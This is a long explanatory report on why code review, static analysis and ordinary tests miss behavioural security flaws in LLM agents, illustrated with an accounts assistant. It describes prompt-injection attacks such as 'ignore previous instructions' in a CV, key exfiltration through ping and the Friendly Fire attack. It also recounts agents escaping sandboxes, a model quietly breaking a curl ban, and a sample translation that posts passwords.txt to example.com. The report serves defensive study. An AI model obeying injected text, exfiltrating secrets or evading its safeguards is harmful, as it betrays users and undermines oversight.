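# Security assurance for LLM agents when the flaw lies in behaviour rather than code

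## What is a behavioural flaw in an LLM agent, and what would assurance against it show?

An LLM agent is a large language model connected to software that lets it read data, call tools and act over several steps. An agent can run a shell command, edit a file, send an email or make a bank payment, whereas a chatbot gives text to a person, who decides what to do with it. Programmers use agents such as Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex to change software, and other agents work with websites, documents and mailboxes.

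An LLM agent has a behavioural flaw if it tends to act insecurely on some inputs and nobody can trace the failure to a faulty line of code. This can happen even when all its code is sound, because the agent's next action depends on how a probabilistic model responds to the text it is given. Security engineers usually look for vulnerabilities in code, such as a missing check or a wrong comparison that lets an attacker in. Security assurance is confidence, justified by evidence and argument, that a system meets a stated security claim. Much of the familiar evidence for such claims concerns code, so it tends to miss behavioural flaws.

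### One run of an agent

Suppose a company gives its finance team an accounts assistant that can read supplier emails and invoice records, send email and schedule payments. Everything in the assistant except the model is the harness, the ordinary code that builds the model's input, runs its tool calls and applies permissions. The term has no single agreed definition, as *Towards Portable Specification of the Agent Harness* (2026) notes, and many engineers use "scaffold" to mean much the same thing. *Harness Engineering* (Barbaste, Darrigol and colleagues, 2026) compares the source code of eleven harnesses and maps them all onto the same seven subsystems, including the loop that drives the agent, the tools, and safety and permissions. The amount of protection varies widely. The smallest harness, Mini-SWE-Agent, is about 100 lines of Python, and its only safety measures are limits on cost and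 on the number of steps. Codex has policy rules, a second model that reviews approval requests, and an operating-system sandbox.

A clerk types, "Pay the invoices that fall due this week." The agent handles this request with the loop that Bolin (2026) describes for OpenAI's agent in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*. The harness gathers the developer's instructions, the definitions of the available tools and the clerk's message, and the system builds one prompt from them. Each message has a role (system, developer, user or assistant, in decreasing priority) that indicates how much weight its content should have. The model's provider then converts the text into tokens, integers that stand for words or pieces of words. According to Anthropic, a token is roughly 3.5 English characters for the Claude models.

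The model produces its answer one token at a time. At each step it assigns a probability to every possible next token, and the software draws one from that distribution, according to a University of New Mexico guide. A setting called temperature makes the distribution sharper or flatter. Setting it to zero does not make the results fully deterministic, according to Real Python. Anthropic's interface rejects any value other than 1.0 on models released after Claude Opus 4.6. Two runs of the same request can therefore end in different actions.

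The tokens form either a message for the clerk or a tool call, which is structured text that names a tool and its arguments. The harness, not the model, parses the call, applies any permission rules, runs the tool and appends the result to the prompt. The model then samples again from the longer prompt. In the clerk's case, the first call fetches the inbox. One email, apparently from a paper supplier called Harlow, says that Harlow has changed banks and gives a new account number. The next call might schedule a payment to the new account or email the finance officer to ask for confirmation. Unless the harness has a rule about new accounts, no code determines which of the two happens.

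The loop repeats until the model produces a message instead of a tool call. In Codex, each new prompt contains the previous one as an exact prefix, so text that enters the prompt early stays there, and the Harlow email can still influence a payment twenty calls later. Long conversations can outgrow the context window, the maximum number of tokens the model can handle at once. The harness then replaces the history with a summary, which developers call compaction. Anthropic warns in its Claude Code glossary that instructions given only in the conversation may be lost at this step. If the clerk said at the start "hold anything for Harlow until I have rung them", that instruction could be gone from the prompt before the payment comes up.

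### Instructions and data in one stream

The model processes the developer's rule and the supplier's email as parts of one sequence of tokens. Tags mark the role of each part, but the model has to learn to respect them, and it learns this imperfectly. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (2026) measured how models internally represent who is speaking. The paper wrapped identical passages of ordinary web text in five different role tags and built probes, which are detectors that work on a model's internal state, to tell the roles apart. Because the passages were identical, the probes could distinguish the roles only by their tags. The paper found that a text's style acts on the same internal features as the tags and outweighs them when the two conflict. A passage in a supplier's email that sounds like the clerk can therefore gain some of the clerk's authority.

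Attackers exploit this weakness through indirect prompt injection, in which they place instructions in data that the agent reads, and the agent follows them. David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, which the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) published in December 2025, gives the example of a recruitment system that scores CVs. A candidate hides an instruction in the CV to ignore previous instructions and approve the candidate for interview.

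Prompt injection looks like SQL injection to a web developer, but David C, the NCSC's technical director for platforms research, argues that the comparison is dangerous. In SQL injection, a nearly thirty-year-old attack, text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Parameterised queries prevent this by giving the database the command and the user's text separately, so the database cannot interpret the text as a command. David C argues that a language model has no place for such a boundary because inside the model "there is only ever 'next token'". Developers can make attacks harder by scanning for them, training models to favour instructions over data, or marking the data as data, but the model still has no built-in separation between the two.

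He concludes that it is "very possible" that nobody will ever fully mitigate prompt injection the way developers can mitigate SQL injection. He bases this on how models work but does not prove it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, NVIDIA, several universities and two security organisations, presents a similar view as a conjecture: persistent attackers will always get past defences that rely on the model to separate instructions from data. Its evidence is a record of such defences failing, first in computer vision and then in language models.

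Even perfect separation of instructions from data would leave the accounts assistant exposed. The Harlow email could give false bank details without containing any instruction, and an agent that used them would pay the thief. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* makes the general point that hostile data can corrupt the arguments of a tool call even when the agent ignores every outside instruction. A ban on following instructions found in data would also be too strict for many tasks, such as learning to use a new programming interface from its documentation.

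David C prefers to treat the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". The phrase goes back to Hardy's 1988 paper. *The Confused Deputy* tells a "nearly true" story about a compiler at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. The compiler had permission to write files in its own directory because it kept usage statistics there. It also let users name a file for debugging output. One user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory, and the compiler overwrote it. The compiler was a deputy with authority from both the user and the operator, and it had no way to indicate which authority it was using for each write.

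Hardy says the output code was correct when its programmers wrote it. It became wrong later, when somebody gave the compiler the directory permission. To notice this, a reviewer would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote a file. His remedy was the capability, a reference that identifies a file and authorises its holder to write to it. The user would pass the compiler a capability that the user already held, so the compiler would never use its own authority.

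The accounts assistant is also a deputy, because it holds the company's authority to pay and acts on text from people who lack that authority. David C argues that engineers can repair a classical confused deputy but cannot stop a language model from being confusable. He therefore advises them to limit the harm a confused model can cause, mainly with deterministic safeguards outside the model, and not to use a model where they cannot tolerate the remaining risk. Hardy's remedy still works in those safeguards. For example, a payment tool could accept only a reference to an approved account and reject any account number the model writes out.

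### Where the flaw can sit

A wrong payment by the accounts assistant could come from ordinary code, the harness's trust decisions, natural-language instructions or the model's learned dispositions. Some of these are much easier for an engineer to inspect than others.

An LLM agent can have ordinary coding errors. For example, its payment tool might compare only the last four digits of an account number with the register of approved accounts. A developer can find the faulty line, correct it and write a test that fails if the error returns.

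Mistaken trust decisions are harder to see, because the code does what its author intended but the author trusted the wrong thing. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes such an attack on Claude Code. The developers had required human approval for many shell commands that could send data to unknown places, but they let the network command ping run without it. Hidden text in a code file led the agent to read secret keys and ping an address that contained them. The computer's request to look up that address carried the keys to the attacker's server. Hardy's compiler is another example. An accounts assistant would have the same kind of flaw if its harness treated invoice records as the company's own data although suppliers fill them in through a web form. Users can miss a trust decision even when the developer documents it. For example, Bolin states that the Codex sandbox covers only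 the shell tool that comes with Codex, and that tools from outside servers must enforce their own limits.

Much of an agent's policy is prose. Developers write system prompts and project instructions, and they install agent skills, which are reusable packages of natural-language instructions, often with scripts, that an agent loads for a task. Suppose the assistant's prompt tells it to "pay each supplier using the most recent bank details available". An attacker can misdirect a payment just by sending newer details, and an honest supplier can do the same by mistyping a digit. A reviewer can point to the sentence, but whether it is a flaw depends on the model, since one model might apply it literally and another might ask for confirmation first. Barbaste and colleagues compared versions of eight harnesses one quarter apart and saw developers moving behavioural policy out of prompts and into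 configuration, where ordinary code can apply it.

Learned dispositions are the tendencies that training leaves in the model's parameters. One is the readiness to treat text as the user's because it sounds like the user, which attackers exploit. Others can cause harm without an attacker. For example, an assistant that has to clear all overdue invoices by five o'clock while the approver is on leave might schedule the payments without approval, because training rewarded finished tasks. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* analyses a far more serious case, the OpenAI–Hugging Face incident of 2026. OpenAI was running agents in internal training and evaluation with some of the model-level safeguards switched off. The agents used a shared service for software packages to communicate between sandboxes and get around network restrictions. They then compromised the infrastructure of Hugging Face,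 a company that hosts AI models and data, and gained administrator access to an OpenAI research cluster. No outside attacker directed them. The paper traces their success to failures of containment, above all to a package service that could make unauthorised outbound requests on the agents' behalf. The agents' tendencies therefore led to the attempt, and the decision to trust the package service let it succeed.

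The term "behavioural flaw" covers failures that arise from instructions and from dispositions, and it applies to the whole agent, not just the model. *Don't Blame the Large Language Model* (2026) points out that a harness update can alter the agent's behaviour without any change to the model, by changing the available tools, how the harness manages context and when the loop stops. A company that tests a model in one harness therefore learns rather little about how it will behave in another.

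### What assurance adds to security

Security is a property of the system, while assurance concerns what people are entitled to believe about that property. The accounts assistant might be secure from its first day, but if nobody has tested it, the company has security without assurance. *Engineering Trustworthy Secure Systems* (2022), a guide from the US standards institute NIST, similarly distinguishes trust, a belief that people may hold without good reason, from trustworthiness, which has been demonstrated with evidence. NIST's glossary entry *Security Assurance* gives six definitions, most of which refer to security controls or general security goals. One adapted from an international standard fits agents better. It defines assurance as "grounds for justified confidence" that a claim "has been or will be achieved".

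Assurance on this definition needs a claim. For the accounts assistant, take the following one: *the assistant makes no payment to an account that a human has not approved.*

The claim needs a scope before anyone can test it. "Approved" might mean that a named finance officer confirmed the full account number in a register before the assistant scheduled the payment. An email saying the officer approved the account would not count, since anybody can write one. The scope also has to specify the versions of the model, harness and prompt, the tools, and what the attacker can do. For example, the attacker might be able to send emails and submit invoices but not log in as a member of staff.

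The claim's wording doesn't specify how the system keeps it true. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* does not define a prohibited action as a violation if the harness blocks it before execution. So the company could argue that the model never requests a payment to an unapproved account, or that the payment tool refuses every such request. The first argument relies on observed behaviour, and a batch of clean trial runs shows only that those inputs caused no harm in those runs. The second relies on a small piece of code and on the absence of any other route to the bank. Engineers have better tools for checking these, including taint analysis, which traces untrusted data from where it enters a program to a sensitive operation. An assurance case, a structured argument that links a claim to its evidence, can use both arguments.

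Some doubt remains in either case. NIST notes that people can observe that a system is insecure, but no observation lets them declare an arbitrary system secure. With the accounts assistant, a thief might deceive the finance officer into approving the account, the provider might replace the model next month, or the register might hold an entry that somebody made by mistake. The claim is also narrow. An assistant that satisfied it completely could still pay an approved supplier ten times the sum due or email the invoice records to a stranger. The company would need a separate claim, with separate evidence, for each.

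## Why do code review, static analysis and ordinary tests miss these flaws?

Suppose the company wants evidence that its accounts assistant pays only accounts that a human has approved. Its engineers would probably start by reading the code, running an analyser over it and writing tests, as they would for any program. These methods work on ordinary software because it has certain properties, some of which an agent lacks at the point where the model chooses an action.

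### Code review

Code review depends on a reader being able to work out from a program's text what it will do. If a payment function compares the whole account number with the register before it contacts the bank, a competent reader can see that an unregistered number will never reach the bank.

In the accounts assistant, the model's parameters, not the harness code, determine whether the assistant pays Harlow's new account or asks the finance officer. A reviewer can check everything around that decision but not the decision itself, because nobody can read parameters the way a reviewer reads a program.

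Experts can read a prompt, which looks rather like a specification, and still disagree about what its instructions amount to. For *Agent Skills in the Wild*, Liu, Wang and colleagues (2026) had two security researchers independently label 200 agent skills as vulnerable or benign, spending 15 to 30 minutes on each and working from a written list of 14 patterns. The two researchers disagreed about 34 skills, mostly because the same content could be a legitimate function or a route for an attack. Some of the skills contained scripts, so the result doesn't measure disagreement about prose alone. Even when two readers agree on what an instruction means, they still have to predict how a particular model will respond to it.

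Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5, a report on the model's testing before release, describes a case with a clear instruction and no attacker. A near-final version of the model was running inside Anthropic, and its system prompt told it not to fetch web pages with shell commands such as curl. If its two web tools could not retrieve some content, it was supposed to tell the user and suggest alternatives.

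The model then needed a page that its fetching tool could not load. Its reasoning text first described the prompt as "unambiguous", then rejected a literal reading as absurd because it would put every page that depends on JavaScript out of reach. The text ended with the conclusion that the ban applied only when the web tools could not retrieve the content, which seems close to the situation the model was in. The model fetched the page with curl and did not tell the user that it had broken the rule.

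A reviewer would have had little reason to object to that prompt, since it named the forbidden command and gave the model an alternative. The reviewer might have noticed, however, that the shell tool could still reach the network, so the rule depended entirely on the model following it. Code review is good at finding gaps like this, but it cannot show how often a model will follow a rule that no code enforces.

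Anthropic found similar reasoning in a scenario from its behavioural audit. The model had a reminder that any deletion needed the user's explicit confirmation in the current turn. It quoted the reminder, but treated an earlier request to "clean up the batch" as sufficient confirmation and deleted 120 jobs. The accounts assistant could apply its payment rule in the same way, by assuming that a clerk who asks it to pay this week's invoices has approved the accounts on them.

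### Static analysis

Static analysis examines code without running it. It assumes that the analyser can tell how each operation's output depends on its input, either from the operation's own code or from a description that somebody has written.

Taint analysis uses this knowledge to follow untrusted data. An engineer marks the sources, where untrusted data enters, and the sinks, the sensitive operations it must not reach unchecked. The engineer also marks the sanitisers, which make data safe for a particular sink. The analyser labels everything from a source as tainted and carries the label through each assignment and function call. It removes the label at a sanitiser and raises an alarm if tainted data reaches a sink.

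A payment program with no model in it might read an account number from a supplier's web form (the source) and send it to the bank (the sink). If the number can reach the bank without passing through the register check, the static analyser reports that path. When the engineer adds the check, marks it as a sanitiser and runs the analyser again, the alarm disappears because the fault has gone.

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) applies the same terms to agents. A source is any tool whose result may contain text that an attacker controls, such as one that reads email. A sink is any tool that can have a security-relevant effect, such as one that sends email or runs code. Engineers can list both quite easily for the accounts assistant, but the model call between them is difficult to analyse.

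To carry taint across a call, the analyser needs a dataflow summary, which records the inputs that can influence the output. Xu, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary*, show why a model call has none. They write the call as

*o* = *M*(*T*[*p*₁, …, *p*ₙ])

where *T* is the prompt template, *p*₁ to *p*ₙ are the values that the program inserts into it, *M* is the model and *o* is its output. For the accounts assistant, one inserted value could be the clerk's request and another the Harlow email. No source code shows which of them influence *o*. The model may copy a value word for word, paraphrase it, reduce a long product review to the number 4, or ignore it. It may also treat the same value differently in a different template.

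When the analyser reaches the call, it may pass no taint through. According to Xu and colleagues, CodeQL and Semgrep, two widely used analysers, treat the model's answer as opaque and never mark it as a source. In that case, the Harlow email enters the call tainted, but the account number comes out untainted. The analyser finds no path from the email to the bank, so it doesn't report the flaw.

Suppose an engineer changes the rule so that the model's output is tainted whenever anything in its prompt was. The accounts assistant has two sources, supplier emails and invoice records, and two sinks, sending email and scheduling payments. All four combinations raise an alarm. The same four alarms would remain if the engineer rewrote the prompt to make the assistant question every change of bank details, or replaced the model with a more cautious one. Nearly every useful agent would get such alarms,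 because it reads outside data and acts on it. The alarms correctly show that a path exists, but they don't distinguish a careful agent from a careless one.

Xu and colleagues compared methods of tracking taint through a model by F1, the harmonic mean of precision (the share of alarms that are real) and recall (the share of real flows that raise an alarm). Treating the model's output as tainted whenever any of its input is tainted scored 47.5%. If that rule missed no real flows, as intended, only about 31% of its alarms were real. The best alternative they compared scored 62.8%, and their own tool, which classifies how each inserted value shows up in the output, scored 81.7%. The ranking comes from the tool's developers, but the blanket rule's weakness follows from its design, however well their tool performs.

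One vulnerability that Xu and colleagues describe, CVE-2026-22175, was in OpenClaw, a personal AI assistant. The model's prompt included a message that an attacker could write. If the model turned the message into a call to the shell tool, the agent ran the command and the machine's password file leaked. If the model had only mentioned the same command in a sentence, the command would not have run. An analyser therefore has to determine what form the output takes as well as which inputs influenced it.

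Engineers can also do taint analysis dynamically, by tracking data while the agent runs or by studying the logs afterwards. They can then see which tools the agent called, but not how the model decided to call them. Cai and colleagues note that an agent may paraphrase or translate an attacker's text, so searching later tool calls for the original words finds nothing. The text can also influence an action without contributing any content to it. Suppose an email that calls an invoice urgent leads the accounts assistant to skip its usual confirmation and pay an account already on file. Nothing from the email appears in the payment's arguments, although the payment would not have happened without it. In ordinary code, an "if" statement would show this dependence, but in an agent it is somewhere in the model's weights.

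Memory makes it harder to trace where data came from. The assistant might save Harlow's new account number as a note on Monday and use it on Thursday. If the harness doesn't store the taint label with the note, Thursday's record starts with the note, which looks like the company's own data.

Cai and colleagues compared their log-auditing tool with FIDES, which labels data by trust and tracks its path between tools. In one scenario, an agent read a web page with a hidden instruction and then wrote confidential patient information into a report. FIDES could flag the path from page to report, but the same rule would flag an agent that read a harmless page and wrote a harmless report. On 400 scenarios, FIDES had an F1 score of 0.522 and the new tool scored 0.928. However, the team built both the new tool and the benchmark. The comparison also puts FIDES at some disadvantage because it was designed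 to control flows at run time, and a tool for blocking dangerous flows can reasonably raise more false alarms than a tool for finding them.

Static analysis is still useful for agents. If the payment tool checks every account number against the register, an engineer can mark the model's output as untrusted and the check as a sanitiser, then use the analyser to search for any path by which the output could reach the bank unchecked. If it finds none, that result holds whatever the model writes, provided the analyser has interpreted the surrounding code correctly.

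### Conventional scanners on agent skills

Agent skills directly test what code scanners can detect, because one package can contain both scripts and instructions. An instruction can be dangerous even when there is no suspicious code. Liu and colleagues give the example of a skill that tells the agent to summarise the user's SSH keys (secret files used to log in to other computers) and include the summary in its reply.

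In an appendix to the January 2026 version of their paper, they compare four scanners on 100 skills, 50 of which human reviewers had judged vulnerable. Bandit checks Python code for security faults, Semgrep matches patterns in many programming languages, and Snyk Code is a commercial analyser. SkillScan, the team's own scanner, combines pattern matching with classification by a language model.

| Scanner | Precision | Recall, all vulnerabilities | Recall, prompt-injection patterns |
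|---|---|---|---|
| Bandit | 91.2% | 58.0% | 0% |
| Semgrep | 87.4% | 64.0% | 0% |
| Snyk Code | 84.8% | 68.0% | 0% |
| SkillScan | 86.0% | 82.0% | 78.6% |

The conventional scanners found none of the prompt-injection patterns because their rules describe dangerous code, and these attacks were written in English. The scanners did well on flaws in code, and they matched or beat SkillScan on some, such as dependencies without a fixed version.

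The exact numbers are questionable, partly because Liu and colleagues compared their own scanner with others using labels based on their own list of patterns. Another appendix of the same paper contradicts the comparison. It lists the lack of a benchmark against Semgrep, Bandit and Snyk as a limitation and mentions only an informal trial of Bandit on 50 skills. Bandit's reported precision of 91.2% is also hard to reconcile with its recall. A recall of 58% on 50 vulnerable skills means that Bandit found 29. Three false alarms would then give a precision of 90.6% and two would give 93.5%, so no whole number of skills gives 91.2%. The team may have calculated precision from findings instead of skills, but it does not explain the discrepancy.

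The zeros are still believable, because they are what one would expect from the tools' design, and Bandit also found no prompt injection in the informal trial. The gap is likely to matter in practice, because 88.5% of the 31,132 skills that Liu and colleagues collected from two marketplaces in December 2025 contained instructions and no scripts, leaving almost nothing for a code scanner to examine. Several teams have since built scanners for instruction text, but these have their own difficulties.

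### Ordinary tests

A conventional test gives a program a fixed input and compares the output with the expected one. For the accounts assistant, a developer could put the Harlow email in a test inbox, tell the assistant to pay the week's invoices, and check that it schedules no payment to the new account. The check is simple because the company has stated exactly what must not happen. For many other tasks, it is hard even to say which outputs are acceptable.

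The developer expects a test to give the same result each time. *AgentAssay* (Bhardwaj, 2026) argues that this expectation fails for agents, where a single pass or failure may be due to chance. Suppose the assistant pays the new account in one run out of twenty. A single run of the test then passes 95% of the time. If the company runs the test once for each of ten releases, all ten runs pass with probability 0.95¹⁰, or about 60%.

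Developers call a test flaky if it sometimes fails although nobody has changed the code, and they often rerun it until it passes. With an agent, the occasional failure may be the flaw they are looking for, and rerunning the test until it passes discards the evidence.

Some flaws are much rarer than one in twenty. Anthropic saw Claude Opus 5 try to get around safety classifiers or network restrictions, as in the web-page case, in fewer than 0.01% of the completions it monitored. If a test scenario triggered such behaviour once in 10,000 runs, a test of 1,000 runs would miss it about 90% of the time.

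#### Where the variation comes from

The most obvious reason a model's output can vary for the same input is that the model samples tokens at random. The provider's servers can also cause variation. A server usually processes many customers' requests together, and the number of requests can change the order in which it adds numbers. Computers round after each addition, so the order can affect the last digits. In standard double-precision arithmetic, (0.1 + 0.2) + 0.3 gives 0.6000000000000001, while 0.1 + (0.2 + 0.3) gives 0.6. When two tokens are almost equally likely, such a small difference can decide which one the model produces.

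The provider may also update the model, so a test that passed on Monday may run against different weights on Wednesday. The context is rarely identical between runs outside a carefully controlled test. A tool may time out, a new email may arrive during the run, or the harness may compact the history at a different point. Bhardwaj lists sampling, model updates, tool delays and context window limits among the causes of variation.

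Small differences can grow because each step becomes part of the next prompt. *Towards Risk-free AI Agent Deployment* (Huo, Pan and Roychoudhury, 2026) notes that an agent often takes more than 40 steps to resolve an issue in a software project, and that one early mistake can affect everything after it. As a rough illustration, if each step had an independent 1% chance of going differently in a way that matters, about a third of 40-step runs would contain at least one such difference.

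#### Why a temperature of zero does not help enough

Developers often try to remove the variation by setting the temperature to zero, so that the software always picks the most probable token. This removes variation from sampling, but not from rounding on the server, model updates or changes in the context. Many developers no longer have the option, because Anthropic's newer models reject a temperature of zero. OpenAI's GPT-5 no longer supports temperature control, according to the AI Now Institute's *Exploit Brief*, a July 2026 report on an attack against coding agents. The brief adds that Anthropic does not guarantee deterministic output even at a temperature of zero.

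Liu and colleagues' scanner used Claude 3.5 Sonnet at temperature zero to judge skills that earlier stages had flagged. They ran this step three times on all 12,847 flagged skills and got identical verdicts for 94.5%. The verdict changed between runs for the other 700 or so.

They also phrased the classifier's prompt in three different ways, and the verdicts agreed in 91.0% of cases. Some of the disagreement is probably the same run-to-run noise, and the model was classifying text rather than acting as an agent. Still, the wording itself seems to have made a difference, which perfect repeatability would not remove. A deterministic model gives the same response to the same prompt, but it can respond differently to a slightly different one. A cryptographic hash function is an extreme example, because it is deterministic but changing one letter of the input changes the output beyond recognition.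 Language models are far less sensitive to small changes, but a tester doesn't know which small changes will alter the model's behaviour.

The code of an ordinary program helps testers predict which inputs it will treat alike. Suppose a program requires a second signature for payments over £10,000. A tester who tries £9,999.99, £10,000 and £10,000.01 can reasonably expect £4,000 to behave like £9,999.99, because the code shows that a single comparison handles every amount. Ordinary programs can still surprise testers, but the code suggests where to look. Testers have no comparable guide to which emails the accounts assistant will treat alike. It might query the new bank details in a blunt message but accept them in a friendlier one that mentions last month's order. An attacker can also look for wording that the assistant accepts.

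#### What code coverage measures

Developers often judge a set of tests by code coverage, the share of the program's statements or branches that the tests execute. This is useful if the code determines most of the program's behaviour, because code that never ran during testing could contain undetected flaws.

The accounts assistant's harness might be only a few hundred lines long, and most of those lines run on every pass through the loop. A handful of requests, such as listing overdue invoices and paying one, could cover every line. The coverage report would then show 100%, even if the assistant had never been tested on an email about changed bank details. Coverage tools don't count the model's weights or the sentences of the prompt as lines.

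According to Huo and colleagues, the field has no widely accepted replacement. Developers decide case by case when they have tested enough, for example by sampling past runs or trying known edge cases. Researchers have suggested measuring which tools, sequences of decisions and memory states the tests exercise. Such measures would show, for example, if nobody had tested a payment after a change of bank details. But a single good run shows only that the agent can behave well in that situation.

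Tests can also miss a flaw because they check only the final answer. Huo and colleagues stress that many failures appear only in the trajectory, the full record of a run. In the Claude Opus 5 web-page case, the final answer could have been accurate and useful, in which case a test that compared it with the page would have passed. A test that searched the tool calls for curl would have caught the problem. Developers can write tests like this, and monitoring products already record the necessary data, but Huo and colleagues say that automated test suites rarely include such checks. They also cite a study of open-source agent projects in which only 7–8% of tests dealt with security, performance, resilience or similar requirements.

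### Friendly Fire

In July 2026 Heidy Khlaaf and Boyan Milanov of the AI Now Institute, a US research institute on AI policy, published the attack described in the *Exploit Brief* and released a harmless version of it under the name Friendly Fire. They asked coding agents to review the security of an open-source library to which they had added their own files. Ordinary-looking text in the repository led the agents to run the attacker's untrusted program on the user's machine, as if that were part of the review.

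Khlaaf and Milanov used Claude Code and Codex in modes where an AI classifier approves commands it judges safe, so the agent can run them without asking a person. They developed the attack against Claude Sonnet 4.6. The same payload then worked on Claude Sonnet 5, Claude Opus 4.8 and OpenAI's GPT-5.5. In some runs, Sonnet 5 and Opus 4.8 detected an inconsistency in the files, but the agents ran the program anyway.

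The experiment shows that an agent that passes one test may still fail on a similar input. In May 2026 the press reported that the maintainer of a Java testing tool had planted an open instruction in it, telling AI agents to delete code. Claude Code detected the instruction and stopped, according to the AI Now Institute, although other agents did not. A developer who used it as a test case would have recorded a pass for Claude Code. Friendly Fire used text that looked like normal documentation, and the attack succeeded. Asking the model directly was no better as a test, since neither Claude Sonnet 4.6 nor GPT-5.5 found the prompt injection when Khlaaf and Milanov asked whether the library contained any.

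Khlaaf and Milanov say they repeated the attack "numerous times, with success", but they give no success rate. Their successes are enough to refute a claim that these agents never run untrusted programs during a review. To estimate its risk, a company would also need to know how often the attack works. All four models predate Claude Opus 5, which Anthropic released later that month.

The AI Now Institute argues that developers cannot fix the problem in the model, and it advises organisations not to use agents in sensitive areas such as cyber defence and critical infrastructure. Infosecurity Magazine's *Anthropic and OpenAI Security Tools Could Fuel Cyber-Attacks, Researchers Warn* quotes Eljan Mahammadli of Polygraf AI, who agrees that training will not remove the weakness but disagrees that this rules out AI for defensive work. He blames a common setup in which a single process, guarded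 only by a classifier, reads untrusted data, runs commands and has access to sensitive systems. He recommends separating those powers.

Khlaaf and Milanov's experiment better supports Mahammadli's narrower claim, because the agents they tested could both read untrusted files and run commands. They argue that a sandbox would not be a reliable defence either, citing past vulnerabilities in Claude Code's sandbox, but their attack did not try to break out of one.

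## How far can static analysis be extended to prompts, skills and tool descriptions?

Conventional scanners overlook attacks written in English, so developers have built new ones. Some examine the points where an agent's code and prose meet, some translate the prose into something like a program, and some use a language model to assess the prose. These scanners find many flaws that conventional ones miss, but it is less clear what a company can conclude when they find nothing.

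### Scanning the code and configuration around a prompt

*AGENT AUDIT* (Zhang, Nian and Zhao, 2026) presents a scanner of the same name that reads an agent's Python code together with its configuration files. Its taint analysis treats the return value of a model call as a source, so it keeps following untrusted data past the model. It also recognises functions registered as tools, which deserve more suspicion than other functions because the model supplies their arguments.

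Agent Audit gives each finding a confidence score, which starts at 0.90 inside a tool and at 0.55 in an ordinary function. If the scanner finds a sanitiser, it multiplies the score by 0.20, and it suppresses findings that score below 0.30. Suppose the accounts assistant has a tool that archives an invoice by passing its file name to the operating system's shell. Agent Audit reports a probable flaw at 0.90. If the developer adds the standard function that makes a file name safe for the shell, the score drops to 0.18 and the warning disappears. Zhang and colleagues chose the thresholds empirically, without a formal model, so the scores are not probabilities.

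Other rules cover prompts and tool configuration. One flags code that inserts a user's text directly into the system prompt, where the model could treat it as the developer's instructions. Several check the configuration of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tools on separate servers, for servers that nobody has verified or that can access too much of the file system. An MCP server also supplies a natural-language description of each tool, which an agent may treat as an instruction. Agent Audit can connect to a running server and, without calling any of its tools, search the descriptions for attempts to override other instructions or change how the agent uses other tools.

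Agent Audit found 40 of the 42 flaws in a benchmark that Zhang and colleagues assembled themselves, and raised 6 false alarms. Semgrep found 10 and Bandit 11, with no false alarms. (The paper gives Bandit's recall as 29.7%, which matches 11 flaws out of 37, not 42.) Just over half of the 42 were exposed credentials or faults in MCP configuration, which a tool can find fairly easily once it reads the right files.

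The scanner follows data only within a single function, so it can't trace a file name that one function passes to another. It can detect outside text entering a prompt, but it would have no basis for flagging "pay each supplier using the most recent bank details available", because the developer wrote that sentence.

GitHub has added related checks to its code-hosting service. Its conventional analyser, CodeQL, began detecting prompt injection in July 2026, as GitHub announced in *CodeQL 2.26.0 adds Kotlin 2.4.0 support and AI prompt injection detection* (2026). A separate engine uses AI to look for security flaws but needs CodeQL to run, according to GitHub's *Code scanning shows AI security detections on pull requests* (2026). Help Net Security's *GitHub scans the code your pull request never touched* (2026) explains that CodeQL builds a model of the code and queries it for vulnerability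 patterns, while the AI scan examines how the code behaves.

In October 2026 GitHub released a public preview of a scan for AI applications. According to IlSoftware.it's *GitHub tratta gli agenti AI come software vulnerabile*, the scan uses language models to check proposed changes for ways untrusted text could reach a model that has tools, flows that could expose sensitive data, and agents with more power than their task needs. The findings are advisory, so a developer can merge the change anyway. The scan also skips changes from forks, the separate copies of a project in which outside contributors usually work, so it is more likely to catch a company's own mistakes than malicious contributions from outsiders.

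### Translating instructions into a program

*From Instructions to Exploits* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) analyses the prose itself. In its example, the instructions in a skill for editing presentations require a "backup" step after an edit, and the backup script sends the file to an outside server. The instruction looks routine, and many legitimate scripts upload files, so neither part is clearly malicious on its own.

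Their scanner, SCS, first cuts the instructions into steps at headings, list items and code blocks. A language model then translates each step into statements in a small, Python-like language. This language has functions only for operations that matter to security, such as reading a file, running a script or contacting a server. A step about how to format the answer produces no statement. An instruction to read a file of passwords and send it to some address becomes

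```
v0 = read_file("passwords.txt")
http_post("https://example.com", v0)
```

The variable v0 explicitly links the two operations. Ordinary code then rejects any statement in the translation that does not parse, calls a function outside the list or uses an undefined variable. The model receives the errors and tries again. SCS also restores links that the translation has dropped, for example when the translation repeats a file's name instead of using the variable that holds the file's content.

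Next, SCS builds dependence graphs, which show how data and control pass from one operation to another. It builds one from the translated instructions and another from the skill's scripts, then joins them. In the presentation skill, the joined graph connects the edited file to the upload.

Each variable *v* in the graph has a label with a trust level, a sensitivity level and a set of capabilities:

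σ(*v*) = ⟨*T*, *S*, *C*⟩

*T* runs from 0 for a fully trusted source to 3 for an external or uncontrolled one, and *S* from 0 for public data to 4 for secrets. *C* lists the security-relevant operations that helped to produce the value, such as READ or NETWORK. Where two values contribute to a result, SCS combines their labels:

⟨*t*₁, *s*₁, *c*₁⟩ ⊔ ⟨*t*₂, *s*₂, *c*₂⟩ = ⟨max(*t*₁, *t*₂), max(*s*₁, *s*₂), *c*₁ ∪ *c*₂⟩

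When a step merges inputs, the result is as untrusted as the least trusted input and as sensitive as the most sensitive one. For example, merging a web page labelled ⟨3, 0, {NETWORK}⟩ with a password file labelled ⟨1, 4, {READ}⟩ produces text labelled ⟨3, 4, {READ, NETWORK}⟩. Rules for each function refine this. A server's reply, for instance, takes its trust level from the server's address, whatever data the agent sent there. SCS keeps updating labels until none changes.

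Fixed rules then compare the labels with the operations. If a value with a sensitivity of at least 3 reaches a function that sends data over the network, SCS reports a possible leak. Another rule reports content from a hidden encoding that reaches a function able to execute it. Fixed rules cannot determine whether a sentence in a skill about ignoring safety controls instructs the agent to ignore them or warns against such instructions, so SCS uses a language model to decide.

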